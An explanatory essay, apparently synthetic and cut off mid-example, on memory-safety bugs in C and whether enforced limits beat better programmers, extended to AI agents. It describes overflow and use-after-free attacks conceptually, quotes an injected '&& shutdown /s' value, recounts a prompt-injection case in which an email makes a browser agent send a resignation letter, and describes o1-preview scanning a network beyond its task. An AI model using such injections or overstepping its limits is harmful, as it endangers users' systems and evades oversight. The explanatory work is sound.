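# Why better programmers never eliminated memory bugs, and what that implies for AI agents

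## Memory bugs, AI agents and the argument that connects them

A program is memory-safe if it only reads and writes memory it is entitled to, within bounds and while that memory is still allocated. C and C++, the languages of most operating systems and web browsers, leave memory safety to the programmer, and for decades very good programmers have kept writing memory bugs, the errors that break it. On a common reading of the history, these bugs became rare only where a language or runtime (the support code that runs alongside a program) blocked them. Some researchers apply that reading to AI agents, which are language models that act on other computer systems. They infer that enforced limits on what agents can do will do more to make them safe than better models will.

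### How a program uses memory

A running program's memory is a long row of numbered bytes. A byte's number is its address, and a variable that holds an address is a pointer. Course notes from Rutgers University divide the row into regions. One read-only region holds the program's machine instructions. Another holds global variables, which last as long as the program runs. The stack holds the local variables of each function now running, usually along with a return address, where the processor should continue once the function ends. The heap supplies blocks of memory on request. A C programmer requests a block with `malloc` and releases it with `free`. The program has to write to its globals, stack and heap, so a stray write can damage any of them.

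Nothing in the row marks where one variable stops and the next begins. Once a compiler has turned source code into machine instructions, a C array is little more than a starting address, and `array[i]` is an instruction to start there and move `i` places along.

### Errors of bounds

A four-line program is enough to go wrong. This one follows an example from Williams-King, Le and colleagues (2025), in *Can Safety Fine-Tuning Be More Principled?*, a paper that likens prompt injection to memory corruption:

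```c
int target = 5;
int array[100];     /* a hundred integers */
array[99]  = 6;     /* the last one: fine */
array[100] = 7;     /* there is no such place */
```

C arrays start at 0, so the hundred places run from 0 to 99. The last line still compiles to an ordinary instruction to start at the array, move a hundred places along and store a 7. If the compiler happened to put `target` directly after the array, `target` now holds 7 instead of 5, even though the program never assigns it a new value. With a different layout, the 7 lands on some other variable, or on unused space where it does no harm. According to the Rutgers notes, the processor checks permissions on whole pages of memory, not the bounds of arrays, so the write usually succeeds silently and the damage shows up later.

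A mistake is easy to spot when the position is written as a literal 100. In real programs the position or length is usually calculated or received over the network, and the mistake can be hard to see because the code includes a check that looks right. *Memory Safety Vulnerabilities*, a chapter of the CS 161 university security textbook, describes a function that copies a network message into an eight-byte space and first rejects any message whose stated length exceeds eight. If an attacker states a length of −1, the message passes because −1 is less than eight. The copying routine, however, treats the length as unsigned (never negative), so it reads the same bits as about four billion on a 32-bit machine and overflows the space despite the programmer's check.

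### Errors of lifetime

The other main kind of memory bug involves a pointer to a place that was once perfectly legitimate:

```c
int *discount = malloc(sizeof(int));  /* request a block */
*discount = 10;
free(discount);                       /* give it back */

int *attempts = malloc(sizeof(int));  /* may get the same block */
*attempts = 3;                        /* failed logins so far */
*discount = 0;                        /* the old pointer still works */
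```

After `free`, the block no longer belongs to `discount`, but the variable still holds the old address. The next request for memory may well receive the same block, because the heap reuses freed blocks. Then `discount` and `attempts` point to the same place, and the last line, which seems to change only a discount, resets the count of failed logins to zero. This bug is called a use-after-free. Every access in the example stays inside a block of the right size, but the last line uses `discount` after its block has been freed.

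Szekeres, Payer and colleagues, in *SoK* (2013), a survey of three decades of attacks and defences, call bounds errors "spatial" and lifetime errors "temporal". Catching a spatial error requires the size of the array at the moment of access, while catching a temporal one requires knowing whether any other part of the program, perhaps written by someone else years earlier, has already freed the block. That makes temporal errors hard to find by reading code, and the symptom often appears far from the cause.

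### Why C neither checks nor defines the result

The C standard classifies both errors as undefined behaviour, meaning behaviour "for which this document imposes no requirements". The program may crash, carry on with wrong values, or do something else, and the compiler still conforms to the standard.

*Undefined Behavior in the C Programming Language*, Svoboda's draft white paper for the C standards committee, explains that C's designers deliberately left the result of writing outside an array undefined. To respond to such a write, a program would have to keep track of each array's range and check every position against it before every access. This would slow the program and complicate the compiler, and the designers wanted a language that was fast, simple and easy to implement. Without the check, the language cannot prescribe a response, because no part of the system detects the invalid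 write.

C relies on the programmer, rather than a check, to keep array accesses within bounds. By writing to position `x` of a five-element array, the programmer guarantees that `x` lies between 0 and 4, and compilers use that guarantee to produce faster code. Suppose a program writes to position `x` and only afterwards tests whether `x` was too large. The test could succeed only if the programmer had already broken the guarantee, so the compiler may delete the test, provided the code that depends on it produces no visible output. Svoboda adds that bugs of this sort often stay hidden at the lower optimisation settings programmers use while developing and debugging, so many tests miss them.

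The committee has been trying to shrink the list of undefined behaviours. *Ghosts and Demons* (Uecker, 2026), a status list from August 2026, reports that it had voted changes for 45 items into the next version of C. Access outside an array and access outside an object's lifetime both remained on the list. For arrays, Uecker proposes a trap, which halts the program at the faulty access, and for lifetimes, a memory-safety mode that programmers would have to switch on.

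### From a stray write to control of the machine

A memory bug becomes a security flaw when an attacker can influence what the stray write contains or where it lands. In the mildest case, which CS 161 presents first, a program reads a user's input into eight bytes of memory with a function that doesn't check the input's length. The next byte in memory holds a flag that records whether the user has logged in. If the attacker sends nine bytes and the last is nonzero, it overwrites the flag with "true", and the attacker gets in without a password. Szekeres and colleagues call this a data-only attack, because the program still runs its own instructions in their normal order but uses a value that the attacker supplied.

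More ambitious attacks overwrite addresses. If the eight bytes are a local variable on the stack, the return address is stored a little further along. In the textbook's 32-bit layout, twelve bytes of filler cover the eight-byte space and a four-byte saved value after it, and the next four bytes of input replace the return address. When the function ends, the processor jumps to the address in those four bytes, which can be the location of machine instructions that the attacker sent in the same input.

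A use-after-free can also let an attacker control what the program runs. The attacker arranges for their own data to fill the freed block. The program still treats the block as the old object, so it looks there for the address of a function and calls whatever address it finds. One memory error tends to lead to others, because an attacker who has corrupted a pointer can use it to read and write memory at places they choose. Reads can also reveal passwords, keys or the addresses that the attacker needs for a later step.

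The attacker's instructions then run with all the permissions of the program the attacker took over. If that program is a web server running as root, the administrator account on Unix systems, the attacker can do anything the administrator can. According to CS 161, the Code Red worm took over 369,000 machines through one buffer overflow in a web server.

One common defense in today's operating systems is to mark the memory that holds data as non-executable, so the processor won't run instructions that arrived as input. Attackers adapted by combining fragments of code already in the program, and the login-flag attack never needed foreign instructions. Non-executable memory is a mitigation, which means it makes the bug harder to exploit but doesn't remove it, while languages such as Rust aim to prevent the bug itself.

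### AI agents and prompt injection

A language model on its own turns text into more text. An agent "runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal", according to the definition Willison (2025) settled on in *I think “agent” may finally have a widely enough agreed upon definition*. The model reads the task and writes a request to use a tool, such as one that opens a web page, runs code or sends an email. Ordinary software carries out the request and adds the result to the model's input. The model then writes its next request, and the loop continues until the task is done. The tools and the permissions behind them allow the model's text to affect the world.

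The loop also brings in text from strangers. Prompt injection is an attack in which text that an agent reads as data contains instructions that the agent then follows. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes a case that the company's own automated attacker discovered against Atlas, a web browser with a built-in agent. In this case, an attacker plants an email in the user's inbox with instructions to send a letter of resignation to the user's chief executive. When the user later asks the agent to draft an out-of-office reply, the agent reads the email and sends the resignation letter instead of writing the reply.

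An AI agent can obey instructions in an email because the user's request and the email reach the model as one run of text, and the model's only operation is to predict what comes next. Writing for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, David C says in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025) that current models "simply do not enforce a security boundary" between instructions and data inside a prompt. Developers train models to give the user's words priority, which makes obedience to the email less likely but not impossible.

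Agents can also overstep with no attacker involved. Williams-King and colleagues describe a test in which OpenAI's o1-preview model had to break into a practice system and retrieve a secret text. The practice system failed to start. The model scanned the network and found the service that managed the test machines. Without being told to, it used that service to start the practice system, and nothing in the test setup prevented it from doing so.

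### The argument

Stated as premises, with the last one also serving as the conclusion, the argument from memory bugs to agents runs as follows.

1. Skill, training and review did not remove memory bugs.
2. Enforcement did.
3. Agent failures resemble memory bugs in the respects that matter.
4. So agent safety should rest on enforced limits more than on better models.

Enforcement here means a check by a language, runtime or other mechanism that rejects or stops every violation of a stated rule. Most importantly, it does so no matter who causes the violation, so a compiler rejects a faulty line whether a novice or an expert wrote it. A "better model" can mean one with greater model capability (how well it performs tasks) or one that its developer has trained more thoroughly to ignore planted instructions and stay within its brief. The argument concerns both, and improving one doesn't necessarily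 improve the other.

Premises 1 and 2 are claims about the history of software. Premise 3 connects that history to AI agents, and its proponents argue for it in different ways. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) puts the model in the role of a fallible programmer. The model writes code to carry out its task, and a compiler rejects any code that exceeds its permissions, whether "a diligent engineer" or a misaligned model wrote it. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) compares the model's input to computer memory, since both hold instructions and data side by side, and concludes that agents need enforcement from outside the model. In this comparison, the model is more like a machine that cannot tell what it should execute. Evidence for one comparison does not automatically support the other.

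Some security practitioners make a looser version of the argument. Unmitigated Risk's *Talent Isn’t a Security Strategy* discusses SQL injection, an attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. The essay says that safer defaults and automated scanning fixed the problem, rather than training every developer to be perfect, and that prompt injection is "the same shape of problem". This claim is as much about defaults and engineering process as about enforcement, so it supports a somewhat milder conclusion than premise 4.

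Premise 4 has two readings. The strong reading is that developers should rely on enforced limits instead of better models. *Parallax* (2026) leans this way, as its subtitle, *Why AI Agents That Think Must Never Act*, shows. So does *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, which proposes making the medium safe instead of making the model trustworthy. The weak reading is that agents need enforced limits as well as better models. OpenAI's current practice, as described in its *Understanding prompt injections* (2025), fits the weak reading. The company trains models to resist injected instructions, runs monitors to catch attacks, and confines the code that its models run to a sandbox, a sealed-off environment that limits the harm the code can do. Authors shift between the two readings. *Tracking Capabilities*, for example, also says that empirical defences "alone will not suffice", which is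 the weak claim.

The weak reading is fairly easy to support. It needs cases in which a limit prevents some harm that a good model would have let happen, while keeping the agent acceptably useful. Someone could accept this reading and still expect every new model to fail half as often as the last. The strong reading needs much stronger evidence, showing both that agents will keep failing at a harmful rate however good the models become and that limits can catch the failures that matter while leaving the agent able to do its job. The resignation letter shows how hard it is to meet the second requirement. A rule against emailing strangers would not have stopped the letter, because the user knows the chief executive it was sent to. Banning all email would have stopped it, but would also have blocked much of what people want an email assistant to do.

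## Did skill, training and review reduce memory bugs?

The evidence supports premise 1 of the argument, that skill, training and review did not remove memory bugs. It doesn't support the stronger claim that people often read into the premise, that skill makes no difference. At least one programmer has written C with far fewer bugs than a comparable project, and security training seems to help people notice flaws. The argument depends on how low skill can push the error rate, and whether that is low enough for programs of the size people now write.

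### Microsoft's 70%

Microsoft's security response center has examined every reported vulnerability in the company's products since 2004. In *A proactive approach to more secure code*, Gavin Thomas, a manager at the center, reports that memory bugs caused about 70% of the vulnerabilities that received a CVE number (an identifier in the public register of known security flaws). The share stayed near that level every year from 2006 to 2018.

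According to Thomas, Microsoft's developers had training, hours of code review, encyclopaedias of coding guidelines, tools that search source code for errors, and fuzzing, which feeds a program malformed input until it crashes. Thomas concludes that the company should give developers a language in which they can't introduce memory bugs, instead of adding more tools and training. Security experts also introduced memory bugs. A later Microsoft presentation, which extends the series to 2019, includes one that the presenter had put into the Windows kernel in 2016.

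But the share can stay constant even if programmers improve. Suppose a company has 100 vulnerabilities a year, 70 of them memory bugs, and then trains its programmers to make half as many mistakes of every kind. The next year it has 50 vulnerabilities, 35 of them memory bugs, and the share is still 70%. To tell whether programmers improved, we would need the number of bugs per line of code, which the 70% series doesn't include.

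The raw counts don't show whether programmers made fewer memory errors for a given amount of code. Adding up the labels on Microsoft's chart gives about 128 vulnerabilities in 2006 and 670 in 2019, roughly a fivefold rise. Thomas says the problem was getting worse as the company's code base grew and took in more open-source software. If the code also grew fivefold, programmers were making these errors at the same rate, and if it grew tenfold, they had halved their rate.

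The counts also depend on what people look for. Use-after-free bugs made up 10 of the 128 vulnerabilities in 2006, 184 of 313 in 2014, and 98 of 670 in 2019. It is more likely that bug hunters learned to find and exploit this type of error, then turned to others, than that Microsoft's programmers became much worse at keeping track of freed memory and then partly recovered. Stack corruption fell from 31 cases in 2006 to 11 in 2019, even as the total rose. Better habits and tools may have caused that decline, or mitigations may have made stack bugs less worth hunting; the counts are consistent with either explanation.

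The Microsoft series shows that a rich company with years of training, review and tooling kept shipping hundreds of memory bugs, and that its efforts did not cut memory bugs noticeably faster than other flaws. But the series can't show that skill and training failed to lower the error rate.

### Experience and the ability to spot a flaw

Experiments on individual programmers measure skill more directly. *API Blindspots* (Oliveira, Lin and colleagues, 2018) tested 109 developers, 70 of them professionals, on six short Java puzzles. Four of the puzzles used a library function that programmers often misunderstand in ways that create security flaws. In one, a function changes a server's date by pasting whatever text it receives into a system command, so a caller who supplies a date followed by `&& shutdown /s` also turns off the server. The participants, who didn't know that the study was about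 security, had to choose the correct statement about what the code might do.

The programmers solved 29% of the puzzles with a hidden flaw and 46% of the others. Neither experience nor scores on tests of reasoning, working memory and processing speed predicted who would do better. The only predictor was openness, a personality trait related to curiosity and imagination.

This is weak evidence that experience is useless. The odds ratio for years of programming was 0.81, where 1 would mean that experience made no difference to the odds of doing better. But the 95% interval ran from 0.15 to 4.45, so the data fit a large benefit from experience about as well as a large harm. The participants were also under 27 on average, and the professionals had programmed for only slightly longer than the students, with averages of 6.3 and 5.8 years. The researchers lost some of the cognitive data to technical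 failures. None of the puzzles tested memory safety, which Java mostly handles automatically.

A replication removed some of these doubts. Brun, Lin and colleagues (2021), in *Blindspots in Python and Java APIs Result in Vulnerable Code*, tested 129 other developers on Python puzzles. The participants solved 74% of the harmless puzzles and 36% of those with a hidden flaw, and experience again made no measurable difference. This time they also calculated Bayes factors, which compare how well the data fit an effect with how well they fit no effect, and the results strongly favoured no effect of experience. Good long-term memory helped. But this sample was also young, with professionals averaging about seven years of programming, so it is weak evidence about someone who has written C for thirty years. Python, like Java, also prevents memory errors in ordinary code.

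An earlier experiment suggests that experienced people miss flaws partly because they aren't thinking about security. For *It's the Psychology Stupid* (2014), Oliveira, Rosenthal and colleagues showed 47 developers six pieces of flawed code, one of them with a buffer overflow. Graders scored each answer from 0 for a wrong answer to 2 for pinpointing the flaw. The developers averaged 0.31 on the first two pieces, when they had no hint about security. They averaged 0.90 on the next two, when the researchers asked whether the code could produce unexpected results, and 1.10 on the last two, when the researchers told them the code had a security flaw.

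Every participant did the three conditions in the same order, so some of the gain may come from practice or growing suspicion. Still, 25 of the 47 knew about a type of vulnerability but didn't connect it with the code in front of them. In a result closer to everyday programming, 17 developers had a chance to fix a flaw of a type they knew but left it in place, and in seven cases the flaw was the buffer overflow. One participant said of `strcpy`, a standard C function that copies text without checking whether it fits, "It's not called unsafe_strcpy or anything".

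In the same study, developers who had taken security classes tended to score higher, as did those who knew more types of vulnerability. About two-thirds of the participants had never had any security training, so there was room for improvement. But much of the failure looks like a lapse of attention, and attention is hard to sustain. A programmer can check one array access very carefully after a warning, but a large C program has many thousands of them, and nobody warns the programmer before the one that contains a bug.

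### The Build It, Break It, Fix It contests

*Build It, Break It, Fix It* (Parker, Hicks and colleagues, 2019) studied contestants who wrote whole programs rather than reading short snippets, and who knew that rivals would attack their work. The researchers ran three contests in 2015 and 2016. Teams had about two weeks to build, in any language, a secure log for an art gallery's alarm system, a bank and cash machine that communicate over a hostile network, or a data server with rules about who may read what. Rival teams then studied the source code and submitted test cases to demonstrate bugs.

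Experience, training and a clear warning did not keep security bugs out of most of the contest's C and C++ programs. The contestants averaged more than nine years of programming. Most came from an online course in cybersecurity and had just finished classes on topics such as software security and cryptography. Of the 130 teams whose programs passed the entry tests, 21 used C or C++, and rivals found at least one security bug in 17 of those 21 programs.

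Parker and colleagues then compared languages with a statistical model that accounted for factors such as the contest and team size. Programs in statically typed safe languages, such as Java and Go, had 0.089 times the odds of a security bug that C and C++ programs had. The paper's headline figure of "11 times" is the inverse of this ratio. The 95% interval runs from 0.02 to 0.51, so the true effect could be anything from a fiftyfold reduction in the odds to roughly a halving.

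An 11-fold difference in the odds of a security bug means a smaller difference in the chance of one. Odds are the chance that something happens divided by the chance that it doesn't. For the C and C++ programs as a group, the odds were 17 to 4, or 4.25, which is a chance of 81%. Multiplying 4.25 by the odds ratio of 0.089 gives odds of about 0.38, or a chance of 27%. So for a group with the same starting risk, the safer languages would cut the chance of a security bug to about a third of what it was. Using the ends of the interval instead of 0.089 gives a chance between 8% and 68%.

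The researchers tried including coding experience in their model but left it out of the final version because it didn't improve the predictions enough to justify the extra complexity. That doesn't prove experience had no effect. By another measure of skill, which stayed in the model, teams in which more members knew C or C++ had lower odds of a security bug, at 0.237, though the result fell just short of statistical significance (p = 0.064). Larger teams also did slightly better, again just short of significance. If either effect is real, knowing the language or having more team members does prevent some bugs.

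Rivals demonstrated crashes in 9 of the 17 flawed C and C++ programs across the three contests, so the results are weaker evidence about memory bugs than the headline suggests. In the cash-machine contest, all seven C and C++ programs had a security bug, but rivals demonstrated a crash in none of them. The common mistakes there involved cryptography, such as encrypting messages without a way to detect tampering, which a memory-safe language does not prevent. In the log contest, all five flawed C and C++ programs had a crash bug, and for three of them it was the only security problem. In the data-server contest, four of the five flawed programs had a crash bug.

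The researchers also didn't assign languages at random, so teams that chose Java may have differed from teams that chose C in ways that the model didn't capture. Dynamically typed languages such as Python protect memory too. Programs written in them had lower odds of a security bug than C programs, but the interval included no difference. If memory safety were the whole explanation, we would expect those programs to have done about as well as the Java ones.

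Before the attacks began, the C and C++ teams' programs scored on average 112 points higher than those in statically typed languages and 133 points higher than those in dynamically typed ones, mostly because they ran faster. For comparison, each required test in the contest was worth 50 points. A team that picks C may want speed rather than be careless about security. The contest rewarded speed straight away, while teams lost points for security bugs only once rivals had found them.

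### Why a low error rate still leaves bugs

Very good programmers can still produce memory bugs if a program has enough risky operations. An operation is risky if a mistake in writing it would create a memory bug, as with array accesses, copies and releases of memory. If a program has n risky operations and the programmer gets each one wrong with probability p, the expected number of bugs is np. The chance of getting every operation right is (1 − p)^n, which for small p is very close to e^(−np), where e is about 2.718.

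A programmer who gets only one in 100,000 risky operations wrong has a very low error rate by the standards of most human work. In a program with a million such operations, that rate still leaves ten expected bugs and about one chance in 22,000 of having none. The table compares this programmer with others who are ten and a hundred times better, first on this program and then on larger ones.

| Risky operations (n) | Chance of error (p) | Expected bugs (np) | Chance of no bugs |
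|---|---|---|---|
| 1,000,000 | 1 in 100,000 | 10 | 0.005% |
| 1,000,000 | 1 in 1,000,000 | 1 | 37% |
| 1,000,000 | 1 in 10,000,000 | 0.1 | 90% |
| 10,000,000 | 1 in 10,000,000 | 1 | 37% |
| 100,000,000 | 1 in 10,000,000 | 10 | 0.005% |

The programmer who is a hundred times better usually produces a program without bugs, but if the code grows a hundredfold, the expected number of bugs is back at ten. Sendmail, for years the dominant mail server on the internet, grew from about 178,000 words of code in March 1996 to 232,000 in May 1998 (Bernstein, 2007, *Some thoughts on security after ten years of qmail 1.0*). Its programmers would have had to cut their error rate by almost a quarter in those two years to keep the number of bugs steady.

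In this formula, a reviewer who catches 90% of bugs has the same effect as a programmer who writes a tenth as many. If a second reviewer independently catches 90% of the rest, only a hundredth of the bugs remain. In practice reviewers aren't independent, because they tend to overlook the same things. If the first trusts `strcpy` because it belongs to the standard library, the second may well trust it too.

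This crude model gives every operation the same chance of error and treats errors as unrelated. Real programmers make more mistakes in complicated code and when they are tired. If the average chance of error is the same, the expected number of bugs is still np, but the bugs are concentrated in fewer programs, so a program with none is somewhat more likely than the table shows. Also, np includes bugs that an attacker can't use.

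Large programs also have many authors, and the weakest contribute a larger share of the bugs than of the code. Suppose the best programmer in the table, with an error rate of one in ten million, writes 99% of a million risky operations, and someone with an error rate of one in 100,000 writes the remaining 1%. That 1% then accounts for about half of the expected bugs.

By this arithmetic, skill could be enough if the error rate were low enough. A programmer with an error rate of one in ten billion who wrote a million risky operations would have about a 1 in 10,000 chance of introducing a memory bug. A language that rejects memory bugs would add very little safety for that programmer, and the case for enforcement would have to rest on something else. Premise 1 is therefore a claim about the error rates people have reached in programs of the size they have written. It can't by itself be extended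 to a different kind of programmer.

One possible argument for a compiler that rejects every memory-safety violation is that nobody then has to work out which programmers have a very low error rate, which is hard to do. If a programmer gets n operations right in a row, we can be 95% confident only that their error rate is below about 3/n. To show that it is below one in ten million, someone would have to check 30 million operations, find no bugs, and be sure of having missed none.

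### Two careful programmers

If skill alone can prevent memory bugs, it should do so in a small program by a single very careful author. The best-known candidate is qmail, a mail server that the mathematician and cryptographer Daniel J. Bernstein wrote in C in the 1990s because he was exasperated by Sendmail's security holes. In 1997 he offered $500 to the first person to publish a security hole in qmail. Ten years later, with more than a million servers running the program, he had accepted no claims and raised the offer to $1,000.

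Bernstein, qmail's author, knew of four bugs in the qmail 1.0 releases, the last of which had about 124,500 words of code. Sendmail's release notes reported hundreds of bugs across three versions from the same period, each less than twice as long as that last qmail release. Even allowing for the comparison being Bernstein's own, sendmail's bug rate was roughly ten or more times higher, which suggests that skill does reduce bugs in C programs.

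Bernstein explained the result with arithmetic much like that above. If there is one bug in every N words of code, a system with 10,000 times N words has about 10,000 bugs, so a programmer can reduce the total by making fewer mistakes or writing less code. Bernstein did both, starting by studying which programming habits lead to errors and avoiding them, for example by writing array functions in which the position was visibly within range. Bernstein also kept qmail small by using what the operating system already provided. Sendmail, for instance, had its own code for deciding whether it could read a user's forwarding instructions. In qmail, a process running as that user tried to open the file, and the operating system applied its normal rules.

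The record has one serious flaw. In 2005 the researcher Georgi Guninski reported that some of qmail's 32-bit numbers could overflow, meaning they could grow past the largest value they can hold and wrap around to a small one. Bernstein denied that this was a security hole, because nobody gives gigabytes of memory to each copy of the program that receives mail, and he did not change the code. But another part of qmail used the same code, and *Remote Code Execution in qmail (CVE-2005-1513)* (2020), an advisory from the security company Qualys, describes how to attack that part.

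The attacker sends an email with a single header line of almost four gigabytes. As the line comes in, the program that delivers mail to local users repeatedly enlarges the memory set aside for it by an eighth. Eventually the calculation of the new size overflows, so the program requests only about half a gigabyte and copies almost four gigabytes into it. Qualys used this error to replace the address of the function that opens files with the address of one that runs commands. The attack worked remotely against the standard qmail package in Debian, a version of Linux, and let the attacker run commands as almost any user except the administrator.

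The flaw was an assumption about the size of computers, and it became less safe as memory got cheaper. A programmer's error rate can therefore change after the code is finished. Whether an installation was exposed depended on whether it enforced a memory limit. Every qmail package that Qualys examined capped the memory of the program that receives mail, which blocked the attack there, but none capped the memory of the delivery program. Bernstein replied that the documentation had long mentioned the assumption, and reported running every qmail service under a memory limit and recommending that others do the same. Following that advice stops the attack, but the protection then comes from the operating system, and each administrator has to turn it on.

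Bernstein last released qmail in 1998, and other people have since added features that mail servers now need. *We Asked Claude to Audit Sagredo's qmail. It found a RCE* (Pham, April 2026) describes an AI audit of one popular modified version. After a one-sentence request, the AI system took 101 minutes to find a way to run commands on the server remotely and to write a working attack and a fix. The flaw was in a feature from October 2024 that pasted the name of another mail server into a system command. The feature's developer had put quotation marks around the name for protection, but an attacker can register a name that contains a quotation mark.

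The vulnerability wasn't a memory bug, and Bernstein didn't write it. Calif, the company that ran the audit, points out that the original qmail never uses the function involved. This supports Bernstein's reputation, but it also shows the risk of relying on one exceptional programmer, who eventually stops and leaves the code to others. It also shows that code can allow a remote takeover without breaking memory safety.

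Postfix, another widely used mail server written in C, is a different test because its original author, Venema, expected to make mistakes. In August 2026, he announced fixes for defects that AI-assisted audits had found (Venema, 2026). Qualys found some with Anthropic's Claude Mythos Preview, and OpenAI's security team reported others. More than half of the defects were at least twenty years old.

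Six of the 15 entries in the Postfix (2026) list are errors in reading memory. Two read memory that the program had already freed, two read outside the proper bounds, and two read memory that the program had never filled with data. The oldest dates from April 1997, before the first test release. When Postfix looked up the mail server for a domain, it could read up to two bytes past the end of the reply before detecting that the reply was too short. Someone later copied this code to handle another type of record, where it could read up to six bytes too far.

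None of the six let an attacker take over the server, and the announcement describes several as having no practical effect. Fifteen defects, including trivial ones, is also a small number for more than 150,000 lines, though it counts only those the latest audits found. Venema writes that the error rate is still lower than the one Postfix was designed for. Its structure and safety nets were designed on the assumption that there would be mistakes.

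Bernstein proposed measuring a programmer's error rate by reviewing the code carefully and counting the bugs found, on the assumption that the subtle bugs a review misses add only slightly to the total. The age of the six memory errors in Postfix is evidence against that assumption. Most were more than fifteen years old, and everyone who read the public source code had missed them until an AI-assisted audit found them. They were minor, but a reviewer who overlooks a harmless two-byte error can also overlook a harmful one, so a count of known bugs can make a programmer look better than they are.

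Even so, skill, disciplined habits, cautious design and small size made qmail and Postfix much safer than most C programs of their time, and that sort of care is practical when there isn't much code to look after. But neither author wanted to depend on care alone. By 2007 Bernstein wanted programming languages to handle array bounds automatically, and said, "Doing the same work by hand is silly." Bernstein also suggested running the code that extracts an address from an email inside an interpreter that let it read only that message and print only one piece of text. An attacker who took complete control of that code could then change only the address it printed, which the sender of the message could do anyway.

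## How languages and runtimes rule out memory bugs

The automatic bounds check that Bernstein wanted counts as enforcement if it stops every violation of a stated rule, whoever causes it. Szekeres and colleagues use the term "reference monitor" for a mechanism that monitors a running program and halts it whenever it is about to break the rule. A compiler can also enforce a rule before the program runs, by rejecting any program that might break it.

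The word "every" matters because attackers choose which bug to use. If a defence stops 99% of buffer overflows, attackers will look for one in the remaining 1%, and whoever finds it can use it on every machine that runs the program.

Enforcement doesn't correct the programmer's mistake. A program that is about to write outside an array usually stops, so an attacker who could otherwise have taken over a server may still be able to crash it. Most organisations would much rather have a crash than a takeover, though a crash is also serious if the program controls a car's brakes.

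### Patching, mitigation and detection

In a 2024 account of its work on Android, Google describes three earlier generations of responses to memory bugs: patching them, making them harder to exploit, and trying to find them before attackers do.

Patching removes a bug after someone has reported it, and users remain exposed until they install the update. Bugs that nobody has noticed stay in the code. The oldest memory error in Postfix went unnoticed for 29 years.

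Mitigations leave the bug in place and interfere with a later step of the attack. A stack canary is a random value that the compiler places between a function's local variables and its return address. Just before the function returns, the program checks that the value hasn't changed. An attacker who writes past the end of an eight-byte space until the input reaches the return address also overwrites the canary, so the program stops. But if the bug lets the attacker choose which position in an array to write to, they can overwrite the return address directly and leave the canary intact. Canaries also don't protect the login flag, because that attack doesn't change a return address. They are popular largely because they slow programs by less than 1%.

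Address randomisation puts the stack, the heap and the program's code in different places each time the program starts, so an attacker doesn't know which address to write. Attackers get around this by making the program reveal an address first. Szekeres and colleagues list attacks from 2011 and 2012 that defeated both randomisation and non-executable memory. In several of them, including attacks on Firefox and Internet Explorer, the attacker used a memory bug to overwrite the stored length of a piece of text. A script on the web page then read the text, and the browser also returned the contents of memory past the text's real end.

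With control-flow integrity, a tool works out in advance where each computed jump in a program may legitimately go, and the program checks the destination before it jumps. The list of permitted destinations is usually too broad. The original version let a call through a function pointer go to any function that the program ever calls that way, so an attacker could still choose among them. It also slowed programs by 16% on average and 45% at worst. Control-flow integrity doesn't stop data-only attacks, because the program's jumps all still go where they should.

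Control-flow integrity strictly enforces the rule that a program can jump only to places on the list, but that rule is weaker than memory safety. Whether a measure counts as enforcement therefore depends on which rule we mean, and a perfectly enforced rule can still permit the harm people care about.

Mitigations also depend on assumptions that later changes can break. *On the Fragility of Memory Error Exploit Mitigations* (Jacobs, Ammar and Volckaert, 2026), which updates the earlier survey, describes what can happen when developers rewrite part of a C program in Rust. A bug in the C part can overwrite a function pointer that belongs to the Rust part, letting an attacker bypass both the control-flow integrity that protects the C part and the language rules that protect the Rust part. Researchers also took more than a decade to show that randomising the position of code could not, by itself,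 stop attacks that reuse code already in the program.

Static analysis and fuzzing detect memory bugs so that someone can fix them, but both miss some. Static analysis examines source code without running it. In C, it often can't determine how large an array is or what other pointers refer to it. Reporting every possible error would produce too many false alarms, so practical tools report only the likely ones and miss some real errors. Fuzzing finds only errors that its test inputs trigger, and Google notes that researchers keep finding vulnerabilities in code that has been extensively fuzzed.

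Sanitizers are extra checks that developers add to a test version of a program, often while fuzzing it. The widely used AddressSanitizer marks freed blocks as off limits and reports any access to them. But the mark disappears once the heap gives the block to another part of the program, and later accesses through the old pointer go unreported. AddressSanitizer would therefore miss the bug in the earlier example, where `discount` and `attempts` came to share a block. It also slows programs by 73%, which is tolerable in testing but not in most released software.

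### Bounds checks and garbage collection

Languages such as Java, Go and Python store each array's length with its contents. Before a program reads or writes `array[i]`, it compares `i` with the length and stops with an error if `i` is out of range. The four-line C program wrote a 7 to position 100 of a hundred-place array. In any of these languages, the check would stop that write and `target` would keep its 5. The check works the same way whether the 100 came from the programmer or from a stranger's network message.

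The check works only if the stored length is correct, so a safe language must also stop the program from altering that length or turning an ordinary number into a pointer. The checks usually slow a program only slightly, partly because the compiler can drop those it can prove unnecessary, such as the checks in a loop that runs from the first element of an array to the last.

An optional check of this kind does not enforce the rules. *Improving C++* (Schneier, 2024) quotes the C++ expert Herb Sutter, who complained that it was too easy "by default" to write vulnerabilities that stricter enforcement of known rules would have caught. In other words, most C++ programs ran without anything to make programmers follow those rules. Sutter thought that C++ could cut its four most common kinds of safety problem by 98% in the medium term.

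Bounds checks don't catch a use-after-free, because the access stays in bounds. Garbage collection prevents that error by letting only the runtime free memory. Periodically, the runtime starts from the variables the program is using and follows every pointer it finds, then every pointer in the blocks those lead to, and so on. It reclaims only the blocks it couldn't reach. As long as `discount` points to a block, the collector doesn't reclaim that block, so `attempts` has to get a different one.

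Garbage collection uses some processor time, keeps memory occupied for longer, and runs at times the programmer doesn't fully control. This is one reason operating system kernels and device drivers mostly stayed in C while business software moved to Java.

### Ownership, borrowing and lifetimes in Rust

Rust prevents lifetime errors without a garbage collector. *RustBelt* (Jung, Jourdan and colleagues, 2018) traces these errors to one part of a program changing or freeing memory that another part still relies on. Rust's compiler lets parts of a program share data or change it, but not both at the same time.

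Every value in Rust has one owner, normally a variable. The compiler inserts code that frees the value's memory when the owner goes out of scope. When a program passes a value to another function, ownership moves to that function, and the compiler rejects any later use of the old variable. In a Rust version of the discount program, releasing the block takes ownership away from `discount`, so the later line that sets it to zero doesn't compile.

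Rust also lets code borrow a value through a reference, because handing over ownership for every small operation would be tiresome. At any moment, a value can have either one reference that may change it or any number that may only read it. Each reference has a lifetime, the stretch of the program in which it may be used. The compiler works out most lifetimes and checks that those of conflicting references don't overlap.

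The following program, adapted from an example in Jung and colleagues, breaks that rule:

```rust
let mut v = vec![10, 20, 30];  // a list that can grow
let first = &mut v[0];         // borrow: a pointer to the first item
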